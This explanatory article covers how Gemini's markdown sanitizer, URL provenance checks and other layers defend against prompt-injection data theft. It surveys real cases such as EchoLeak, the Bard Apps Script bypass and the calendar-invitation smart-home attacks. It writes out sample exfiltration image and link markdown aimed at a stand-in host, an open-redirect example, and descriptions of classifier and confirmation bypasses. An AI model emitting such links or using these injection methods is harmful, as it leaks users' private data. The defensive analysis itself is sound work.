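# How Gemini filters images and links to stop data theft by prompt injection

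## How a chatbot's reply can leak private data

Gemini, Google's AI assistant, can read and summarize a user's Gmail messages, Drive files and Calendar entries. Anyone can send the user an email or share a document with them, and a stranger can include instructions that Gemini may follow as if the user had given them. Security researchers call this indirect prompt injection. One of its most often reported uses is exfiltration, which means moving private data to a place the attacker can read.

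An attacker can use the assistant's own reply to steal private data. Planted instructions make the model put private text into the web address of an image or link, and the user's browser sends that text to the attacker when it contacts the address. Google's *Mitigating prompt injection attacks with a layered defense strategy* (June 2025) described a filter that stops Gemini from displaying external images and removes links it classifies as suspicious. The attack was already two years old by then, and most of what a designer needs to know about such a filter comes from those two years.

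### Instructions inside the material

A language model receives its input as one sequence of text. When a user asks for a summary of a web page, the application combines the request, the text of the page and its own standing instructions (the system prompt), and sends it all to the model. Simon Willison, the developer who named prompt injection in 2022, explains in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents* (2025) that models follow instructions anywhere in their input and cannot reliably rank them by origin. *Not what you've signed up for* (Greshake et al., 2023) describes indirect prompt injection and demonstrates it against Microsoft's Bing Chat. The attack is called indirect because the attacker never talks to the assistant, and the attacker's text instead arrives with the material the victim asked about.

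Hiding the text takes little skill. Microsoft (2025) mentions white text on a white background and non-printing characters, and says even a plain text file can carry an injection. Developers have precise rules for preventing SQL injection, a similar problem in which attackers slip database commands into form fields. Rehberger (2024) points out in *Trust No AI* that no such rules exist for prompt injection. Microsoft therefore assumes that some injections will succeed when it designs its products, and tries to stop the harm at a later step.

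### From a planted sentence to a server log

When a browser opens a web address, it sends the address to the website, and websites commonly log the addresses that visitors request. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) explains that anyone who can get private text into the address can read it later in that log.

Chat assistants usually write their replies in markdown, a plain-text notation for links, images and formatting. The chat window turns this markdown into a web page. An image in markdown is written as `![label](address)`.

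Suppose a user has told the assistant that the code for the club's garden gate is 4471, and then asks it to summarize a shared document about the summer picnic. The document contains a sentence in white lettering. It asks for a picture at the end of the summary, with the gate code in place of the blank:

```
In the document:   ![map](https://pictures.example/map.png?note=____)
In the reply:      ![map](https://pictures.example/map.png?note=gate+4471)
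```

The attacker wrote everything up to and including the equals sign in advance. The model fills in only `gate+4471`, where the plus sign stands for a space. The chat window converts the line into an image, the browser requests the file from `pictures.example`, and the attacker's server records a request for `/map.png?note=gate+4471`. The server doesn't need to have a picture, because the code has already arrived by the time the user sees a broken image icon.

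In this sequence, the model only writes text. The browser makes the connection, because browsers fetch images automatically. Ordinary code can therefore inspect the reply before the browser displays it, and a filter like Gemini's works at that point.

The private text can sit in the path of the address or in a subdomain (the part before the main domain name), and Microsoft notes that attackers can encode it in base64, which turns words into a string of letters and digits. Checking only for readable secrets after a question mark would therefore miss some leaks.

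### Zero-click and one-click leaks

The picnic example is a zero-click leak because the data leaves as soon as the reply appears. If the model writes an ordinary link with the same address, the leak is one-click, since nothing leaves until the user clicks the link. The attacker then has to give the user a reason to click, and can do so in the link's label, for example with a request to log in again.

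A link in a chatbot's reply can leak data without a click if the reply appears in a messaging app such as Slack or Telegram. These apps fetch the linked page to show a preview of it, and PromptArmor, a security firm, warns that the preview makes the same kind of request as a click.

Tools can also allow zero-click leaks. *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026) describes the 2025 ShadowLeak attack, in which a crafted email told ChatGPT's Deep Research agent to find sensitive mail and visit a web address that contained it. The agent made the request from OpenAI's servers, so the request did not have to pass through the user's browser. Filtering the displayed reply cannot stop this kind of leak.

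### Three conditions

Willison calls the dangerous combination the "lethal trifecta": access to private data, exposure to content that an attacker can influence, and a way to communicate externally. An attack needs all three. An assistant without access to private data has none to leak, and one that reads only trusted text never receives the attacker's instructions. If the model can't send data out, it may still follow those instructions and collect private data, but the data stays in a chat that only the user can see.

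An email assistant has to read both private data and untrusted content to do its job. Willison's *45 posts tagged “exfiltration-attacks”* therefore describes the third condition for data theft, a way to send the data out, as generally the easiest of the three to remove, and vendors have mostly fixed reported flaws by removing it.

A fixed rule can also stop leaks through images. Microsoft distinguishes probabilistic defenses, which make an attack less likely to work, from deterministic ones, which guarantee that a particular attack fails. A classifier that looks for malicious instructions is probabilistic, and Willison considers even a 95% catch rate a failing grade because an attacker can keep rewording the instructions until something gets through. A rule that no external image ever loads is deterministic because it holds whatever the model writes. But data can still leak in other ways,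 and the rule doesn't stop injected text from changing what the assistant tells the user.

### From ChatGPT to Bard

The image leak became public in April 2023, when the software engineer Roman Samoilenko described it in *New prompt injection attack on ChatGPT web version*. In Samoilenko's version, a web page added hidden instructions to whatever a visitor copied, and the visitor then pasted them into ChatGPT. The attack leaked the chat through an image one pixel wide.

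Johann Rehberger, a security researcher who writes the blog Embrace The Red, reported the same flaw to OpenAI and Microsoft that year. According to the blog's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, Microsoft fixed Bing Chat in May 2023 with a Content Security Policy, while OpenAI began to act only in December. In May 2026, The Hacker News (2026) reported that Permiso Security had found ChatGPT's display still automatically fetching images whose addresses came from pages it had just summarized.

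A Content Security Policy (CSP) is a list, sent by a website along with a page, of the domains from which the browser may load the page's images, scripts and other resources. web.dev's *Content security policy* gives the example of a page that allows scripts only from itself and one Google address; the browser blocks all others. Because the browser enforces the list, text in a planted document cannot override it. Its weakness is that it usually filters by domain. It also governs what the page loads, so it doesn't cover ordinary links that the user clicks.

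Google Bard, the assistant that later became Gemini, used a content security policy (CSP) to limit where it could load images from. In September 2023, when Bard had just gained extensions for reading Gmail, Drive and Docs, Rehberger, Joseph Thacker and Kai Greshake found that it followed instructions in a Google Doc and would display images. The CSP blocked an image from Rehberger's own server but allowed every domain ending in `google.com`. That included `script.google.com`, where anybody can run a small program using Google Apps Script. Embrace The Red's *Hacking Google Bard* describes how Rehberger wrote a program there that accepted requests without a login and copied whatever followed the question mark in its address into a Google Doc. The planted document, disguised as a notice from a legal department, made Bard append the first 20 words of the conversation to that address.

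Rehberger reported the chain on 19 September 2023, and Google confirmed a fix on 19 October. The CSP had not changed and images still appeared, so Rehberger inferred that Google now filtered data out of image addresses.

The Bard case shows that a list of trusted domains is only as safe as the most permissive service on any of them. Owning a domain does not make it safe if outsiders can run code or store data there. Similar gaps have appeared in other products. In January 2026 Willison noted that the email app Superhuman had allowed images from `docs.google.com`, where Google Forms records data sent in a web address. In a September 2025 case, Salesforce's policy still listed a domain whose registration had lapsed, and the researchers registered it themselves.

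### The other Google products

Rehberger found the image leak in four more Google products between August 2023 and August 2024, and Google repaired them in different ways.

Google made the simplest fix in Vertex AI's Generative AI Studio, a tool for developers. Embrace The Red's *Google Cloud Vertex AI* reports that Google stopped turning any links or images into HTML there. Rehberger thought this was probably the best fix for security, at least for a product that does not need pictures. It would be more inconvenient in an email assistant, since people want to follow the links in their mail.

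Colab, Google's online notebook for writing code, had a much weaker protection when Rehberger examined it in November 2023. Its system prompt told the model not to render images, but Rehberger got around that by asking the model to join fragments of text that together formed the text for an image. An attacker's instructions can override those in the system prompt, so code that runs after the model has finished writing has to enforce the rule.

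Google closed the image leak in Colab, but links stayed clickable. Embrace The Red's *Google Colab AI* (2024) found that Colab showed a confirmation page before opening links to other sites but exempted Google domains, the same mistake Bard had made with images. Apps Script links therefore opened with no warning, and one click sent the user's name, email address and notebook code to Rehberger's log.

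In NotebookLM, which answers questions about files that a user uploads, an attacker could leak private data by controlling a single field in a file. Rehberger's test document was a customer list in which one customer had put instructions in the description field of her own record. When the user asked about her, the reply contained an image whose address included another customer's email and code. A second test extracted sales figures from a separate document. A filter therefore has to work even when most of a file is harmless, or when the secret and the instructions are in different files. Rehberger reported the flaw on 4 December 2023 and went public after 132 days without a fix. Google had deployed one by 19 April 2024, according to Embrace The Red's *Bobby Tables but with LLM Apps*. The preview pane beside the chat also displayed images, so a filter has to cover every place where the product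 shows text.

In AI Studio, Google's workbench for trying out its models, Rehberger had only sporadic success with markdown in August 2024. He then asked the model for an HTML image tag, which a browser reads directly, and that worked. AI Studio had no CSP, so the images could come from any server. In his demonstration, an employee's planted performance review made the model write one invisible image for each of the other reviews, with a 60-word summary in each address, so limiting the length of a single address would have done little to prevent the leak. Embrace The Red's *Google AI Studio* says that Google fixed the flaw by showing image tags as text, within 24 hours of a public message to Logan Kilpatrick, who works there. A sanitizer that checks only markdown misses this attack. It has to recognize everything that the display code will turn into an image.

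### EchoLeak

Microsoft 365 Copilot answers employees' questions from their company's email, files and chats. It had several of these defenses when researchers at Aim Labs, part of Aim Security, bypassed all of them in January 2025. *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration* (Ravia, 2025) is the researchers' own account of the attack.

The attack began with an email from outside the company. Microsoft ran a classifier to catch prompt injections, so the researchers addressed the instructions to the human recipient and never mentioned an AI. They repeated the instructions under many headings, such as leave of absence and questions for the personnel department, so that Copilot would retrieve the email for many different questions. The instructions were to provide the most sensitive item in the model's context.

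Next came the link filter. Copilot removed external links in the usual markdown form, with the address directly after the label. Markdown also allows the address to stand on a line of its own, and the filter missed that form:

```
Removed:       [report](https://pictures.example/?note=gate+4471)

Not removed:   [report][ref]
               [ref]: https://pictures.example/?note=gate+4471
```

This let Aim Labs leak data with one click from the user. Putting an exclamation mark in front of the link turned it into an image, which the filter also missed. The filter missed both because it matched only one pattern of brackets. A filter that first runs the reply through the parser the chat window uses finds the link or image in either notation.

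Copilot's CSP still restricted images to a list of nearly thirty permitted sources. The researchers searched the list for a server that would forward a request. A SharePoint address did so, but only if the victim had accepted an invitation to the attacker's site. A Microsoft Teams address, meant for fetching outside content, required no action from the victim. The browser requested an image from Teams, as the policy allowed, and Teams contacted the attacker's server with the secret in the address.

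The "zero-click" attack still required the employee to ask Copilot something, but the question could be routine, and nobody had to open the email or point Copilot to it. In the Bard and NotebookLM demonstrations, by contrast, the user brought the poisoned document into the conversation. The EchoLeak email also told the recipient not to refer to it, for compliance reasons, so Copilot's answer did not cite it as a source.

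According to the timeline in *EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025), Microsoft fixed the flaw on its own servers in May 2025, and the details became public on 11 June. *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* notes that Microsoft rated the severity at 9.3 out of 10, while the US National Vulnerability Database rated it at 7.5. Microsoft knew of no attack on a customer.

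Google published its account of Gemini's defenses two days after the disclosure. It called EchoLeak "not applicable to Gemini", saying that Gemini does not render external images. That rules out the zero-click version, which depended on an image. The one-click version needed only a link that the filter failed to recognize, and Gemini relies on detecting suspicious addresses to stop such links.

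## How Gemini filters images and links, step by step

Google's June 2025 post covers both the Gemini assistant inside Workspace apps, such as Gmail and Docs, and the separate Gemini app. Both use a markdown sanitizer, code that parses the model's reply and removes or neutralizes images, links and HTML before display. Gemini blocks external images and checks links with Google Safe Browsing, which identifies phishing, malware and other unsafe web addresses. In Google's example, a Gmail thread contains an unsafe link, and Gemini replaces it with the words "suspicious link removed" in its summary of the thread. This is called URL redaction.

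Google did not explain there how the sanitizer recognizes a link or what happens to an address that is new to Safe Browsing. A later check matters more for such addresses, and Google describes one in *Mitigating URL-based Exfiltration in Gemini*, a post on Bug Hunters, its site for outside security researchers. The order of steps below is second-hand, taken from a machine-written summary of that post. Most of the benefits and drawbacks are inferred from the design, not stated by Google.

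### Parsing the reply

Code on Google's servers first parses the markdown in the model's reply, splitting it into paragraphs, links, images and other parts much as the chat window would. This prevents the filter from missing links the way Microsoft's filter missed EchoLeak's.

Because this happens on the server, one filter can protect the website, the phone apps and the panel inside Gmail, and a user with an old version of the app still receives cleaned text. The drawback is that two programs now interpret the same markdown, which has several dialects. Some turn a bare web address into a link, while others leave it as text. If the phone app renders a link from notation that the server's parser treats as plain text, the link gets past the filter. A designer can reduce this risk by having the server write new markdown from the parsed parts, in the simplest notation, instead of passing on the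 model's original text.

Parsing also causes a small delay. Chat windows usually show a reply while the model is still writing it, but the server can't check an address until all of it has arrived, so it has to hold back unfinished links and images.

### Images

Next, the filter deletes every image except those with a `data:` URL. An address of this kind contains the picture itself, encoded as text:

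```
External image:  ![map](https://pictures.example/map.png?note=gate+4471)
Data image:      ![map](data:image/png;base64,iVBORw0KGgo...)
```

The first image leaks the gate code, as before. The browser displays the second without contacting any server, so even if the model wrote the gate code into a `data:` image, the code would stay in the chat.

Unlike Bard's content security policy, which Rehberger bypassed with Apps Script, this rule doesn't depend on judging which domains are safe, so an attacker gains nothing by using a new domain or a trusted one that forwards requests.

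The drawback is that the model can't show a photograph from a website or a chart from a newsletter by writing its address. A product that needs such pictures can display them through a separate component that takes the address directly from a search result, so the model can't alter it. The exception for `data:` URLs should stay limited to images, because a `data:` URL can contain a whole web page, including scripts.

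### Links and HTML

The same link can appear in a reply in at least four forms:

```
[picnic](https://club.example/picnic)

[picnic][ref]
[ref]: https://club.example/picnic

<https://club.example/picnic>

https://club.example/picnic
```

The filter converts the different forms into one standard form, so later checks only have to handle one. This matters little in an ordinary chat, but it can annoy someone who asks Gemini to edit a markdown file and wants the links unchanged.

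The same address can also be written in different ways. `HTTPS://Club.example/%70icnic` leads to the same page as the links above, because capital letters make no difference in a domain name and `%70` is another way to write the letter p. A designer comparing addresses has to standardize these details too.

The filter then escapes HTML by replacing characters such as `<` with codes that the browser displays as ordinary text. An HTML image tag then appears on screen as code, as in Google's AI Studio fix. Harmless HTML formatting, such as a tag for underlining, also appears as code. The filter escapes HTML after parsing because one of the four link forms uses angle brackets, and escaping them earlier would break legitimate links.

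### Where an address came from

After these steps, the reply can still contain clickable links, and one of them could carry the gate code. The design therefore looks up each link's URL provenance, a record of where the URL came from.

The possible origins of an address fall into two groups. Search, Gmail and the user's own prompt are non-generative sources, which supply addresses that someone other than the model has already written. The model is a generative source because it can compose a new address, and so is code execution, a tool that runs programs written by the model. For example, a one-line program could join `https://pictures.example/?note=` to the gate code. If the filter treated the result as ordinary tool output, the model could use the tool to disguise an address it had composed.

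Checking a URL's provenance is useful because the attacker has to write the planted email before learning the secret. The complete address, `https://pictures.example/?note=gate+4471`, doesn't exist until the model writes it, so the filter finds no match for it in the user's mail, search results or prompt.

The comparison has to cover the whole address. If it covered only the domain, or ignored everything after the question mark, the beginning of the address in the planted email would count as a match, and the gate code would get through.

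An exact comparison also fails on harmless links, in at least three situations:

- The model shortens an address, for example by dropping `?from=newsletter` from the end.
- It makes a typing error in a long address, such as a link to a shared document.
- It gives the address of a well-known public page that it learned in training and that appears nowhere in the user's material.

If the filter allows small differences between a copied address and the original, an attacker can exploit them. Suppose the filter lets the model delete characters but not add any. The attacker plants an address that ends in the digits 0 to 9 repeated four times, and tells the model to delete digits until only the gate code, 4471, remains. The shortened address passes the filter but contains the code. It is safer for the filter to find the closest address in the user's material and display that original in full, which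 gives the user a working link and discards the model's changes.

If the model can compose an address, save it in a document and read the document again, the address would seem to come from Drive. The filter therefore also needs to keep its record that the model wrote the address.

Checking where a link came from doesn't stop a model from choosing among complete links that an attacker has prepared. Those choices can slowly spell out a secret, as Willison (2026) reported about Anthropic's assistant Claude.

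### Allowlists and other signals

Many links that a model composes are useful, such as a map search for a street address in an email. Gemini's design therefore adds allowlists and other signals to the provenance check. An allowlist is a list of destinations that the filter accepts even when the model composed the URL.

A designer choosing domains for the list has to check whether an outsider can learn which addresses people request there. A well-run reference site may keep its logs private, so a secret in an address would reach only the site's operator. Google Forms does let outsiders learn this, as the Superhuman leak showed.

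An open redirect causes the same trouble. This is a page that forwards visitors to any address included in its own:

```
https://allowed.example/go?to=https://pictures.example/?note=gate+4471
```

The domain is on the allowlist, so the filter accepts the link. When the user clicks, the allowed site redirects the browser to `pictures.example` with the gate code attached. To prevent this, the designer can allow only particular pages on a domain, or refuse addresses with anything after a question mark. Both rules take more upkeep and break more useful links. For example, search pages usually put the search terms after a question mark.

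Google can also block an address pattern quickly, but only after someone discovers the problem. In *Google Workspace’s continuous approach to mitigating indirect prompt injections*, Gavish (2026) classes URL sanitization as a deterministic defense that Google manages through a central Policy Engine. Google's staff can change the configuration without retraining a model. For instance, they can add a regular expression, a formula for matching text, to catch every address that uses a newly reported redirect.

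Checking against a list of bad addresses is deterministic, like the image rule, but it gives a weaker guarantee because it reliably blocks only the addresses and patterns on the list.

*The Trifecta*, a study of Gemini by the security company Tenable, found that Gemini also redirected markdown links to a `google.com` address and cut off suspicious output. Colab's confirmation page relied on a similar redirect. According to Embrace The Red, Colab put `https://www.google.com/url?q=` in front of every clickable link.

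A redirect gives the user a chance to see the real destination. It could also let Google check the address again when the user clicks, since Safe Browsing may have more information by then than when the reply appeared. But the full address, including any secret, still follows `q=`, and the attacker receives it if the user continues. A filter must also remove the redirect before it checks a link, because otherwise every redirected address looks like a link to Google.

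### Four links through the filter

Suppose Gemini summarizes the club's email about the picnic and its reply contains four links. The table shows what would happen to each one if the filter removed every link that Safe Browsing lists as unsafe and every composed link outside the allowlists. These results are inferred from the design, not from a test of Gemini.

| | Copied from an email | Composed by the model |
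|---|---|---|
| **Harmful** | `https://club-login.example/verify`, a known phishing page. Safe Browsing lists it, so the filter removes it. Its provenance is fine. | `https://pictures.example/?note=gate+4471`, on a domain registered yesterday. Safe Browsing has no record of it. The provenance check finds no match, so the filter removes it. |
| **Harmless** | `https://club.example/picnic`. It passes both checks and stays. | `https://maps.example/search?q=river+park`. Safe Browsing has no objection, but the provenance check finds no match. The filter removes it unless `maps.example` is on an allowlist. |

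Safe Browsing and the provenance check catch different links. The phishing address was in the email, so the provenance check gives no reason to remove it. The leaking address is on a domain with no history, so Safe Browsing's reputation check finds nothing wrong with it. Google may list the domain after someone reports it, which would protect later users, but by then the attacker already has the first victim's gate code.

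Only the allowlist lets the filter distinguish the two composed links. Each has a domain, a question mark and some words that the model chose, and neither appears in the user's mail. If the designer leaves `maps.example` off the list, users lose a useful link. Adding a domain with an open redirect would give attackers a way to steal data.

A link to a phishing page created yesterday would pass both checks if Gemini copied it unchanged from an email. The attacker wrote the address in advance, so it can't contain the gate code, but the page could still collect a password if the user types one in.

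*Exploiting Markdown Injection in AI agents*, by the software security company Checkmarx, argues that Gemini can remove a malicious link only if Safe Browsing has already identified it, so an attacker can set up a new domain and persuade the user to click. Checkmarx reported this to Google on 5 October 2025, and four days later Google closed the report as "Won't Fix (Infeasible)". Google also replied that the risk was not severe enough to track as a security bug. Checkmarx accepted that a fix might not be feasible but thought users should be warned.

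The argument holds for a filter that relies on reputation alone. A provenance check on every link the model composes should remove the link that Checkmarx describes, unless an allowlist permits it. Checkmarx does not discuss provenance, and the recorded demonstration in its article shows Microsoft's Copilot Chat, so the article does not establish whether Gemini was applying such a check in October 2025.

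OpenAI recognizes composed addresses differently. According to Embrace The Red, it uses a web crawler, a program that visits public pages and records their addresses, to build a list of existing addresses. The system lets ChatGPT's agents use those addresses and blocks ones created on the spot. This works better than Gemini's approach for public pages that the model remembers from training, because the crawler has probably recorded them. Gemini's approach works better for the private links that an email assistant often handles, such as links to shared documents, because a public crawler should never have seen them.

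### Links removed by mistake

Neither Google's June 2025 post nor its help page for Workspace administrators gives a figure for how often Gemini removes harmless links. On the help page, Google asks users to send feedback if they think Gemini made a mistake. The page also explains that Gemini checks files for suspicious links and prompts before it processes a request. If it finds messages or documents suspicious, it leaves them out and tells the user that it excluded some content for security reasons. A mistake in this check can exclude a whole document instead of one link.

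Public complaints show related problems but not this one. Chromeboard's *Gemini Link Fixer* (2025) describes a browser extension released in October 2025, with 99 users listed. The extension removes a Google search wrapper from links written by Gems, which are customized versions of Gemini. The listing's example is a link to Jira, a tool for tracking work, that fails until the wrapper is removed. If a Gem builds a Jira address from a ticket number, the link is harmless, but a provenance check might wrongly block it. However, nothing in the listing connects the wrapper with Gemini's security filter.

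A user on Google's developer forum reported a similar change in *Bug*. The user had asked the model to tidy some markdown, and a plain link to `https://example.com` came back inside a `google.com/url` redirect. The user suspected that the model itself wrote the redirect, perhaps as a learned pattern, but nobody has established the cause. In another forum complaint, *False Positive Domain Block on Google Gemini Live Browsing (sourceoftrust.com)*, Mayr says that Gemini refuses to analyze their own harmless business website. That complaint concerns browsing, which is separate from removing links in a reply.

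The tests Google has described also would not show how many harmless links the filter removes. Gavish explains that Google runs simulated attacks on Workspace features with a defense on and then off, which measures how many attacks the defense stops. To count wrongly removed links, a team would have to run ordinary requests on ordinary mail and see which harmless links disappear. Counting shortened addresses, typing errors, remembered pages and composed searches separately would help, because each needs a different fix.

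## What the other layers do that the filter cannot

Gemini's link filter acts only on a reply the model has already written. Most of Google's other defenses can stop an attack before it reaches the filter. Some also protect against harm that doesn't involve a link.

### One email, layer by layer

Suppose a stranger emails the user about the club picnic. The email contains instructions in white text for Gemini to end its answer with a link containing the gate code and to delete Saturday's picnic from the user's calendar. The user then asks Gemini to summarize the week's mail.

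Content classifiers are machine-learning models that check the email before Gemini uses it. Google trains them on a catalog of known attacks, which it built with the help of outside researchers. Gemini leaves out whatever the classifiers flag, and gives no answer if nothing else remains. Flagging the picnic email would stop both the link and the deletion.

A classifier makes a learned judgment, so an attacker can look for wording that it misses. EchoLeak got past Microsoft's classifier with instructions addressed to the human recipient. Google says Gmail blocks more than 99.9% of spam, phishing and malware, but that figure doesn't measure how many prompt injections the classifiers catch. An ordinary phishing email may contain no instructions to the assistant, so an injection classifier has nothing to detect. The link filter can still remove the link if Safe Browsing lists it.

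If the classifiers miss the picnic email, Gemini surrounds the email's text with reminders to carry out the user's request and ignore instructions in the email. Google calls this security thought reinforcement. Code can add the reminders every time, but it can't guarantee that the model will follow them, and the attacker can write sentences meant to outweigh them.

The next defense is the model's own training, which Google DeepMind's *Advancing Gemini's security safeguards* (2025) calls "model hardening". An automated system wrote injections that worked on Gemini in realistic tasks with sensitive information, and Google then trained the model to ignore them and answer the original request. A hardened model may ignore malicious instructions in an email that the classifiers missed, whether they ask for a link or a deletion. Hardening also relies on learned judgment, and Google DeepMind acknowledges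 that no model is completely immune.

If the model does follow the email, different defenses apply to the two instructions. Gemini has to use a calendar tool to delete the picnic, and Google gives deleting an event as an example of an action that may require confirmation. Gemini shows the event and asks the user to approve the deletion, which a user who only wanted a summary has good reason to refuse. Code can enforce this step whatever the model has read, but the step fails if the designer forgot to require confirmation for a harmful action or if the user approves without understanding the request.

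Writing a link uses no tool, so Gemini doesn't ask for confirmation. Only the output filter can now remove the link, which it can do because the address with the gate code appears nowhere in the user's mail. But the filter doesn't remove ordinary text. If the email had told Gemini to say that the picnic was canceled, that false sentence would stay in the summary.

Finally, Gemini automatically shows a warning when one of its defenses has stopped something. An attack that every layer misses produces no warning, so users can't assume that a summary without one is safe. A warning can still prevent harm outside the chat, since the original email remains in the inbox with its links intact. Google's *How Gemini Apps help protect users from malicious content & prompt injection* also advises caution with shared chats and with web apps that strangers have made in Canvas, Gemini's workspace for building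 them.

### Harm without a link

In *Invitation Is All You Need!*, Nassi, Cohen and Yair (2025) used calendar invitations to make Gemini open the windows and turn on the boiler in a user's apartment. The invitation contained the attacker's instructions, which entered the conversation when the user asked Gemini about upcoming meetings.

Google already prevented planted text from immediately starting an unrelated tool, according to *Gemini's Secret Affair* (2026), a later study by SafeBreach, the security company where Yair works. The researchers therefore used delayed tool invocation, a technique Rehberger had published. The invitation told Gemini to wait for the user's next harmless message, such as "thanks", and then send the command to the smart-home system.

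This attack didn't require Gemini to display a web address, so even a perfect link filter would have approved the reply while the window opened. Nicolas Lidzborski, a Google engineer who works on Gemini's security in Workspace, discussed the attack in a March 2026 talk. According to *Securing Workspace GenAI at Google* (2026), a summary made from the talk's transcript and slides, Google had protected the user's data but overlooked what the assistant could do in the home.

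Nassi and colleagues demonstrated 14 attacks, including deleting calendar events and streaming video of the user through Zoom. They scored each threat by its likely harm and how easily an attacker could carry it out, and rated 73% high to critical. They rated opening a window as severe because a burglar could climb through it, and an attack on the boiler as moderate.

The researchers reported the attacks on 22 February 2025, and Google responded with stronger confirmations for sensitive actions, stricter handling of web addresses and better classifiers. The researchers estimated that such measures could reduce the risk to between very low and medium. They note that the defenses Google announced in June 2025 were missing or ineffective during their tests, so the study doesn't measure how well the full set works.

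### Approving the wrong thing

Yair then tried to get past the new defenses, this time with messages from apps such as WhatsApp and Slack. On Android, Gemini can read message notifications aloud, so anyone who can send the user a message can put text into the user's conversation with Gemini.

Delayed tool invocation now failed on every attempt. But Gemini would still open a window if it had asked about the window and the user had said yes. Yair inferred that a security check compared the user's last message with Gemini's last reply to see whether the "yes" made sense as permission.

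The new attack, which SafeBreach named Fake Context Alignment, exploited this check. The planted message made Gemini ask a harmless question along with a request for permission, which was in a form that the user didn't understand or didn't hear. When the user said yes to the harmless question, Gemini's software took the answer as permission for the hidden request.

Yair could again open windows and start a Zoom call. Unlike the earlier attack, this one also saved a false name in Gemini's long-term memory and scheduled a daily task that read the user's recent messages. Both changes would remain after the conversation ended, and the memory is shared across the user's devices.

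The Zoom attack also exposed a gap in how Gemini checked web addresses. The tool that opened them blocked any address that Safe Browsing classed as unsafe or didn't recognize, and apparently blocked even addresses on safe domains if they carried extra data. But it followed redirects without asking the user. In the demonstration, which simulated the redirect on a test device, an address on a domain with a clean record made the phone join a Zoom meeting. A designer has to check the final destination as well as the first address.

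Yair reported the findings on 17 August 2025, and on 14 November Google confirmed that improvements to its content classifier had stopped the attacks. SafeBreach published the details on 3 June 2026. The Hacker News (2026) reported no evidence that anyone had used the technique in a real attack.

The fix Google described works on the incoming message, before the user has anything to approve. Google did not say whether it had also changed how Gemini matches a "yes" to an action. If it hadn't, a message worded differently enough to get past the classifier could cause the same problem again.

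In a safer design, the app would write the confirmation question instead of the model. It could show or read aloud a fixed question in the user's language, such as "Open the bedroom window?", and accept an answer only to that question. The user's answer would then apply to the same request the software is handling.

Approval requests wouldn't help if people approve everything out of habit. Lidzborski warned that users check requests at first and then "just become approval bots". The talk proposed tracking the override rate, which is the percentage of AI decisions that people reject. A low rate is hard to interpret, because Gemini may be proposing sensible actions or users may have stopped reading. A team could tell the difference by including a few obviously wrong requests in a trial and measuring how often people approve them.

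### How often attacks still succeed

*Lessons from Defending Gemini Against Indirect Prompt Injections* (2025) describes how Google DeepMind tests Gemini models that use tools to read untrusted data. Some of the test attacks stay the same, while an automated system keeps rewriting others, called adaptive attacks, to beat a particular defense.

Google DeepMind reports that spotlighting and self-reflection worked well against fixed attacks but much less well against adaptive ones. Spotlighting marks untrusted text so that the model can recognize it, and self-reflection has the model check for signs of an attack. A team that tests only with a fixed list of attacks would therefore overestimate both defenses.

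Google DeepMind also reports that model hardening lowered the success rate of attacks without significantly affecting the model's performance on normal tasks.

Outside researchers have since tested Gemini models in four quite different ways:

- *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* (2026), by a team that includes researchers from the security company Gray Swan AI and from Meta, reports on a public competition in which 464 people made 272,000 attempts against 13 models.
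- *DecodingTrust-Agent Platform (DTap)* (2026) includes attacks on agents doing legal work, such as redirecting a confidential email.
- *INFUSE* (2026) measures both whether attacks succeed and whether the model still completes the user's task.
- PromptArmor's *FrontierBreach* adds attacks to long office tasks, such as analyzing a bond portfolio.

| Test | Gemini model | Successful attacks | Other results in the same test |
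|---|---|---|---|
| *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* | Gemini 2.5 Pro | 8.5% | Highest of 13 models; the lowest was 0.5% |
| *DecodingTrust-Agent Platform (DTap)*, legal tasks | Gemini 3 Pro | 56.3% | From 9.5% to 66.2% |
| *INFUSE* | Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite Preview | 41.9% | Average of 19.6% |
| PromptArmor | Gemini 3.6 Flash | 22.4% | Average of 34.9% across the original 21 models |
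| PromptArmor | Gemini 4 Argon | 4.3% | Second lowest of 22 models |
| PromptArmor | Gemini 4 Carbon | 2.4% | Lowest of 22 models |

The rates aren't comparable across tests because the attacks and tasks differ. The competition's 8.5%, for example, counts every attempt, including clumsy ones. In PromptArmor's test, the two Gemini 4 models did much better than Gemini 3.6 Flash. The margins of error for the two Gemini 4 models overlap, so the test doesn't show which of them is safer.

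A low attack success rate can also reflect a model's limitations rather than its resistance to attacks. In *INFUSE*, attacks on Claude Haiku 4.5 succeeded only 8.4% of the time, but the model completed 52.6% of users' tasks when attacks were present, down from 75.0% without them. In the legal tasks, the open model OSS-120B had a lower rate than the GPT models because it could handle less text and missed some of the planted instructions.

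In these tests, the models ran outside the Gemini app, without its full set of classifiers, confirmations and link checks. The results indicate how often a model might follow a planted instruction, not how often Gemini users lose data.

Repetition also helps the attacker. Lidzborski pointed out that the same attack may fail nine times and work on the tenth. If each email independently had a 10% chance of success, there would be a 65% chance that at least one of ten worked. Gemini's rule against external images gives the same result on every attempt.

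### Retraining and fixed limits

Google keeps updating its learned defenses. According to Gavish, staff, automated systems and outside researchers find new attacks, and Google generates variations of them. It uses some of these to retrain its classifiers and reserves others for testing. It also rewrites the instructions it gives to the language models that serve as defenses.

The Policy Engine lets Google update URL sanitization without retraining a model. It also controls user confirmation and tool chaining policies. Tool chaining policies limit which tools Gemini may use one after another. For example, one could stop a malicious calendar invitation from triggering a smart-home command even if the classifiers had missed the invitation.

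Gavish doesn't publish success rates from Google's tests with a defense on and then off, for the link filter or any other layer, so outsiders can't tell how much the filter adds.

Measuring what changes when the filter is switched off could undervalue it. If the classifiers already catch nearly every attack in the test set, the results will change very little. The filter would matter most against a new attack that the classifiers miss, so a team should also test it with the earlier layers switched off. The test set also needs more than variations of known attacks, because these may not resemble the next technique.

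Lidzborski went further and argued that defenders cannot win by filtering inputs. Attackers can encode their text to avoid a filter that looks for certain words, or use synonyms and less common languages to avoid a classifier. If a second language model judges the text, attackers can include instructions for that model too.

The alternative in the talk is to limit what the assistant can do after an injection succeeds. The orchestrator, the code that runs tools for the model, could block requests to outside websites once Gemini has read Workspace data. In the picnic example, Gemini's tools then couldn't send the gate code to a web server, even if the model followed all the instructions in the email. This would also block some useful requests, such as comparing a quote in an email with prices on the supplier's website.

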